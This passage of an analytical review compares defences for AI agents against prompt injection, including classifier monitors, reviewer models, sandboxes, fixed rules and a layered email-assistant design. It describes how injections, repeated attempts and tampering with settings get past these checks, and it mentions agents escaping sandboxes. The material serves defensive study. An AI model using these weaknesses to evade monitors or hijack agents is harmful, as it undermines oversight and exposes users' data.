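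The classifier works in two stages. A quick first stage answers yes or no, and a slower second stage reasons about anything the first one flags. Anthropic measured both stages on a version that ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6:

| Test | First stage only | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
| False alarms on 10,000 real actions by staff | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Misses on 52 real actions that went beyond the user's request | 6.6% | 17% |
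| Misses on 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data | 1.8% | 5.7% |

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user said as consent. For example, a request to "clean up the PR" doesn't authorise overwriting the history of a shared branch. Anthropic later gave the classifier more information about its surroundings, and its miss rate on attacks designed by Apollo Research, an AI safety company, fell from 12% to 7%.

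If the classifier gives no verdict, for example when a request times out, Claude Code blocks the action. If the classifier allows an action it should have blocked, the only remaining defences are the deny rules and an optional sandbox. The sandbox uses the operating system to restrict where shell commands and the programs they start can write files, and which internet domains they can contact. It doesn't cover the agent's built-in tool for reading files, which only the permission rules restrict (University of Vermont, 2026).

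The sandbox had other gaps in May 2026, according to Anthropic. If it couldn't start, Claude Code showed a warning and ran the commands without it, unless an administrator had changed that setting. Its network filter checked the requested domain's name but not the contents of encrypted traffic, so a user who permitted github.com might have given a hijacked agent a place to publish stolen data. Anthropic doesn't consider this sandbox sufficient on its own for fully unattended work, and suggests running the whole agent in a container or virtual machine.

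### Chrome's agent

The planner in Google's browser agent has to read web pages to decide what to do next, which exposes it to injections. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes two other models that don't read the pages. One, the User Alignment Critic, receives only metadata about each proposed action and vetoes actions that don't serve the user's goal. It is similar to the narrow judge that Xiang and colleagues propose. The other, a gating function, decides which websites are relevant to the task.

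The browser then enforces the gating function's decision. In the full design, the agent may read from one set of sites and click or type only on a smaller set. If a page contains an advertisement from an unrelated site, the browser doesn't pass the advertisement to the planner. The first version tracked only the sites on which the agent could act.

Some checks involve no model. Code restricts the web addresses the model writes to known public ones, because an invented address could carry private data. It also compares each destination with a list of sensitive sites, such as banks, and prompts the user before the agent visits one. The agent needs the user's permission to sign in with a saved password, which the model never receives.

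Purchases and messages can happen on any site, so a list of sites can't identify all of them. Parker says the agent "will try to pause" before such actions. *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) makes the firmer claim that Chrome requires human approval before any high-stakes action. Chrome can only do this reliably if it recognises which actions are high-stakes, and on an unfamiliar website it probably relies on a model for that.

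An outside test found weaknesses in this kind of agent. Browsers normally follow the same-origin policy, which stops one website from reading another's content. *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (Roesner and Kohlbrenner, 2026) examined whether a malicious page could use the agent to get around this policy. In early 2026, Chrome's agent met the preconditions for such an attack, which would also have needed a successful injection. Chrome's simpler first version didn't limit what the agent could read, which may explain this result. Roesner and Kohlbrenner carried out the full attack on ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser.

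### OpenAI's and Microsoft's agents

By default, OpenAI's coding agent Codex has no network access, and a sandbox enforced by the operating system limits which files it can touch, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. Codex can work freely inside the sandbox but needs approval to do anything outside it.

In a mode called Auto-review, a separate reviewer model gives that approval instead of the user. According to OpenAI, the sandbox and its limits stay the same, sessions stop for human approval about 200 times less often, and the reviewer approves about 99% of requests. Most requests in ordinary work are probably legitimate, so the high approval rate doesn't show that the reviewer is lax. OpenAI ends the run after repeated denials to guard against an agent that keeps trying requests until the reviewer accepts one.

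OpenAI protects its web-browsing agents with a check on links. It claims only that the check protects against one kind of leak, in which the agent reveals the user's data through the address of a page it fetches. The check doesn't make the page's contents trustworthy. Filters may also be getting less reliable. *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (OpenAI, 2026) reports that the most effective real attacks increasingly resemble social engineering rather than simple commands to ignore earlier instructions.

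Microsoft similarly divides its defences between an injection classifier called Prompt Shields and fixed rules against known leak routes such as image links. Roesner and Kohlbrenner found that Microsoft's Edge browser with Copilot had stronger security properties than Chrome or Atlas but more limited agent features.

The table shows what each design still prevents when its models judge wrongly.

| Agent | Fixed rules decide | Models decide | What remains if the models are fooled |
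|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code in auto mode | Which actions the user's rules forbid, and the sandbox's limits if it is on | Whether most other commands may run | The deny rules and any sandbox. Without them, a command runs with the user's own access |
| Chrome's agent | Which web addresses the model may write, and which listed sites need the user's consent | Which sites are relevant, and whether an action serves the user's goal | The address check and the list. The browser still enforces its site limits, but the attacker's site may be inside them |
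| Codex with Auto-review | What the agent can reach from inside the sandbox | Whether a request may cross the sandbox's boundary | The sandbox, except for requests the reviewer wrongly approved |
| Microsoft's assistants | Whether output may use known leak routes | Whether text contains an injection | The blocks on those routes |

Codex has a stronger fallback than Claude Code by default because its sandbox is already on. Claude Code users can get similar protection but have to set it up.

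It is hard to tell from published tests how much these controls add to the models' own resistance. The outside test of auto mode that Anthropic commissioned in July 2026 also covered other settings. Against GPT-5.6 Sol, 19.03% of attacks succeeded in Codex's Full Access mode and 5.83% with Auto-review, so Codex's controls cut the rate by about 70%. Against Anthropic's latest models, only 0.09% succeeded on average with no extra safeguards, which left auto mode little to prevent. The attacks were optimised against an older Claude model, and the test left out the safeguards built into each company's own browser extension.

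### Would system controls have stopped real attacks?

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* makes the case for system controls by analysing eleven attacks on real products. For each one, it lists the established security principles that the product violated:

| Principle | Attacks that violated it |
|---|---|
| Secure information flow: private data must not reach untrusted places | 11 |
| Least privilege | 6 |
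| Complete mediation: a monitor must check every action | 3 |
| Tamper resistance: the agent must not be able to alter its own controls | 2 |
| Allowance for human error | 2 |

The counts are slightly uncertain because the paper's discussion of two attacks includes principles missing from its table. But they fit the view that an agent needs more than permission rules. All eleven attacks involved data or instructions going where they shouldn't, while only six needed the agent to have excessive permissions.

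The coding agent Amp violated tamper resistance because it could edit the settings file that listed which commands needed no approval. The obvious fix is to prevent the agent from changing that file. This works however an attacker words the injection, and it causes the user almost no inconvenience.

OpenAI's web-browsing agent Operator violated secure information flow because personal data from a site where the user was logged in could reach an attacker's page. The paper rejects asking the user to confirm every change of page and describes information-flow control for such models as an open problem.

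The other cases fall between these two. The paper describes a difficulty with every fix it proposes for the nine attacks in its appendix, such as a loss of useful functions or a policy that nobody yet knows how to write. Some of the fixes are not system-level controls. The paper recommends cleaning the agent's output against an attack on Microsoft's Copilot that hid data in a link, and against another attack that hijacked a user's terminal. This cleaning would be a component-level filter that works by fixed rules.

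The analysis is also retrospective. One researcher, Johann Rehberger, reported ten of the eleven attacks, so the sample depends heavily on what he looked for. Because it includes only attacks that worked, it can't show how often products with better controls resist attack. The cases are good evidence that these products lacked basic protections and that a few simple rules would have prevented some of the damage. They are much weaker evidence that system controls could have stopped all eleven attacks without making the agents less useful.

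### Two objections to relying on system controls

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* gives two reasons not to depend on the model alone, though it accepts that model-level defences can prevent many attacks and that system controls take engineering work and reduce speed and utility. A request in natural language can be ambiguous, so the model may misjudge what the user authorised. The model's behaviour can also change between runs, or when an attacker changes the input. Adding a learned guard doesn't remove this weakness, because an attacker can optimise one piece of text against the model and another against the guard, then combine them.

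The first reason is weaker than the second. A written policy doesn't remove the ambiguity in "send it to the address in Bob's latest email", because someone still has to decide whether an address in forwarded text counts. The policy only makes that decision explicit and its enforcement consistent.

Recent tests support the second reason. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026), Google's Gemini 4 Argon was the most robust model, resisting 87% of attacks when the attacker could send it 150 queries but only 66% at the largest query budget. The attacker, also Gemini 4 Argon, was far more persistent than most real attackers would be. Still, a company that relied on this model alone would have no other defence against the third of attacks that succeeded at that budget. In a December 2025 blog post quoted by Fortune (2025), OpenAI compared prompt injection to scams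 and said it was unlikely ever to be fully solved.

The opposite objection is that no system control will contain a sufficiently capable model, because the model will find a flaw in whatever confines it. The OpenAI–Hugging Face incident, in which agents escaped their sandboxes, strengthened this objection. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* replies that the sandboxes failed because the established principles were not applied at every point, including shared services, and that the incident therefore does not show that containment is impossible.

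This reply is reasonable but hard to test, because almost any escape could be described afterwards as a failure to apply the principles fully. In practice, engineers must apply them fully before a capable model finds the gap. That seems achievable for a small monitor with a narrow job, such as checking one mail tool. It is much harder when containment depends on large, general-purpose services, as the paper acknowledges. The paper also accepts that the controls must leave the agent able to do its work, and that nobody yet knows how to derive suitable policies reliably.

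Neither objection is a good reason to use only one level of defence. A fixed rule still limits the damage from rare failures even if models become very robust, and if models become better at escaping, their training has to prevent some of the harm that the sandbox can't.

### Four defences on a team of six agents

In *Beyond Single-Model Injection*, Paul and Nandy (2026) tested a combination of defences on a team of agents that analyses company filings. An orchestrating agent divides the work among agents for retrieval, code, analysis, compliance and output. Paul and Nandy devised 14 kinds of attack, with 50 texts for each, and counted an attack as successful if an agent acted outside its permitted role. They used GPT-4o, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Llama 3 70B, and reported the highest of the three models' success rates.

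The team already had instructions in its prompts to reject unauthorised requests. Paul and Nandy added four defences:

- Sanitisation checks every message that enters or leaves an agent. It combines a check on format, a limit on length and a classifier that looks for instructions. This is a component-level defence.
- Message signing attaches a cryptographic signature and a record of origin to each message between agents. This is a system-level defence with fixed rules.
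- Privilege scoping gives each agent access only to the tools for its role. This is also system-level with fixed rules.
- Anomaly detection looks for unusual patterns in the messages between agents. It sits at the system level, but it estimates what is suspicious and can be wrong in the same way as a filter.

The table gives the success rate for each type of attack. "Cascading" attacks manipulate the orchestrating agent so that one compromised agent affects the whole team. The last column is the average over the 14 kinds of attack, calculated from the other columns.

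| Defence | User's input | Tool results | Messages between agents | Cascading | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompts only | 19% | 43% | 31% | 28% | 31.2% |
| Sanitisation | 8.4% | 9.5% | 31% | 22% | 18.1% |
| Message signing | 19% | 43% | 2.8% | 18% | 21.0% |
| Privilege scoping | 19% | 34% | 31% | 16% | 26.1% |
| Anomaly detection | 14% | 38% | 24% | 4.5% | 21.7% |
| All four | 3.8% | 4.6% | 1.2% | 3.4% | 3.2% |

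Paul and Nandy report an overall fall from 31.2% to 4.2% for the combination. Weighting their category results in the way that produces the 31.2% gives 3.2% for the combination instead of 4.2%. The drop is large in either case.

Combining defences makes sense because no single one does best against every type of attack. Sanitisation has the largest average effect of any single defence, but it does nothing about messages between agents. Privilege scoping has the smallest average effect. It stopped every attempt to call a tool outside an agent's role, but an agent can still misuse the tools its role requires.

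The study can't show how much each defence contributes to the combination, because Paul and Nandy tested the defences one at a time and then all together, but never removed one from the full set. Anomaly detection, for example, might add a lot to the other three or almost nothing. They also didn't test the three system-level defences together without sanitisation, so the study can't separate the effects of the two levels. The sanitiser itself combines fixed checks with a classifier, and its result doesn't show how much each contributed.

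Message signing proves which agent sent a message, but a deceived agent can still sign a malicious one. Paul and Nandy say the figure fell from 31% to 2.8% because injected text can't forge a signature. That explains why signing stops impostors, but not why it would stop an agent that an injection has taken over. The record of origin may have helped if the receiving agents used it to reject text from outside sources.

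Paul and Nandy refined the attack texts to get past the prompts, and didn't change them after adding the four defences. They expect an adaptive attacker to do better. They report that the sanitiser's classifier wrongly flagged 2.3% of messages, but not how many ordinary tasks the protected team completed.

### A layered design for the minutes

The office assistant could combine five layers to send the March minutes:

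1. A sanitiser removes suspicious instructions from Bob's email.
2. The planner writes the steps before any model reads the email, and names the file to attach. A quarantined model extracts the address, and code accepts only a valid email address as its answer.
3. Before sending, code checks the recipient against the company directory. If the address isn't there, the email waits.
4. The user sees the waiting email, the new address and the passage it came from. Approval covers that exact email and nothing else.
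5. Code writes the final message to the user from a template: "The March minutes went to" followed by the address.

The first layer is component-level, the fourth depends on a person, and the other three are system-level. They would affect the three attacks and the honest task as follows:

| Layer | Attack 1: salary file | Attack 2: outsider's address | Attack 3: false report | Bob's real new address |
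|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sanitiser | Probably removes a blunt order | Probably misses it | May miss a plain statement | Should leave it alone |
| Fixed plan | **Stops it** | No effect | No effect | Lets it through |
| Directory check | Would hold an email to the outsider | Holds the email | No effect | Holds the email |
| User's approval | Not needed | **Stops it if the user checks with Bob** | No effect | Releases the email |
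| Template | No effect | Shows which address the agent used | **Stops it** | Shows which address the agent used |

The fixed plan stops attack 1 even if the sanitiser misses it. Attack 2 depends on the user, because the directory check holds both the outsider's address and Bob's new one for the user's approval. A user who approves without checking will send the minutes to the attacker, but the assistant asks only when the address is new, so the user should be more willing to read the question. If the outsider's address is already in the directory, the assistant sends the minutes without asking.

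The template can't help if the user asks for a summary of the email. The assistant could attribute the claim to its source, as in "a message that Bob forwarded says the April meeting is cancelled". This would give the user some reason to doubt the claim, but no layer would have shown that it was false.

This design suits requests with predictable steps. For a request like "do whatever Bob's email asks", the assistant would have to read the email first and then show the user a proposed plan.

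This example could most easily do without the sanitiser. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) measures what filters add to a fixed policy, in partly simulated tests. Filters alone cut the success rate of a single disguised injection from 62.8% to 6.6%, but an attacker with up to 25 attempts always succeeded. When filters were added to the policy, single attempts succeeded 0.3% of the time. But if the attacker had complete control of the model, 23.1% of attacks succeeded with or without the filters. The filters also reduced the completion of ordinary tasks by 4.5%.

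The simulation assumed that filters weaken as an attacker keeps trying, so the poor result for repeated attempts partly reflects that assumption. The pattern still makes sense, because a filter reduces how often an attack reaches the rules but can't change what the rules permit. For an assistant that receives many crude attacks, that reduction may be worth a small loss of utility.

### A dishonest tool

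All five layers rely on the mail tool doing only what it should. Suppose the company installed a mail tool from an unknown developer, and the tool sends each email correctly but also copies it to a stranger. The minutes would leak even though the plan is correct, the recipient is in the directory, and the call contains nothing suspicious.

Qu and colleagues define tool integrity as a tool doing nothing beyond its declared purpose, so a tool that reads unrelated files or contacts undisclosed servers lacks it. They find that PromptArmor, Task Shield, DRIFT, Progent and CaMeL do not address tool integrity, because these defences are designed for tools that do only what they declare. Progent can check the arguments of a call, and CaMeL can check where they came from, but neither controls what the tool does with them afterwards.

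Agents that install add-ons from open marketplaces face this threat in practice. In the ClawHavoc campaign, attackers tried to steal passwords and cryptocurrency by planting more than 1,000 malicious add-ons in the marketplace for the OpenClaw agent. A separate audit of 42,447 add-ons found at least one security vulnerability in 26.1% of them. Most of these vulnerabilities could be honest mistakes, but attackers may still be able to exploit them.

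A malicious tool can also attack the planner. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* describes tool servers that hide instructions in their tools' descriptions. A planner normally reads these descriptions before it writes its plan, so keeping Bob's email away from the planner would not prevent this attack. The developer would have to treat the descriptions as untrusted, or approve them in advance and block later changes.

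The survey also argues that a control at one layer of an agent can't detect an attack confined to another. The control may still limit the damage. If the mail tool runs on the company's own computer, a sandbox around it could block connections to any server except the company's mail server. Anthropic offers its sandbox software for uses like this, on tool servers and other programs. If the tool runs on its developer's server, the minutes have already left the company when the call arrives, so a sandbox on the user's side can't protect them.

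### Harm the user doesn't notice

Unlike permission rules, filters offer some protection against false or biased reports. Qu and colleagues give PromptArmor partial credit for protecting an agent's judgement, because it can remove an explicit instruction to mislead the user. They give Progent and CaMeL no credit, because both control the agent's tool calls, not its conclusions. Neither kind of defence reliably stops a plain false statement.

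A successful attack may also leave no trace in the agent's reply. *Will the User Ever Know?* (2026) studies injections that achieve the attacker's goal while staying hidden from the user. Defences that add warnings to the prompt sometimes reduced the number of successful attacks, but did not make the remaining ones more visible. A log written by code could show the user an unexpected email. In attack 3, however, the log would contain only the email the user asked for, so the user would probably have to learn from an attendee that the April meeting had gone ahead.
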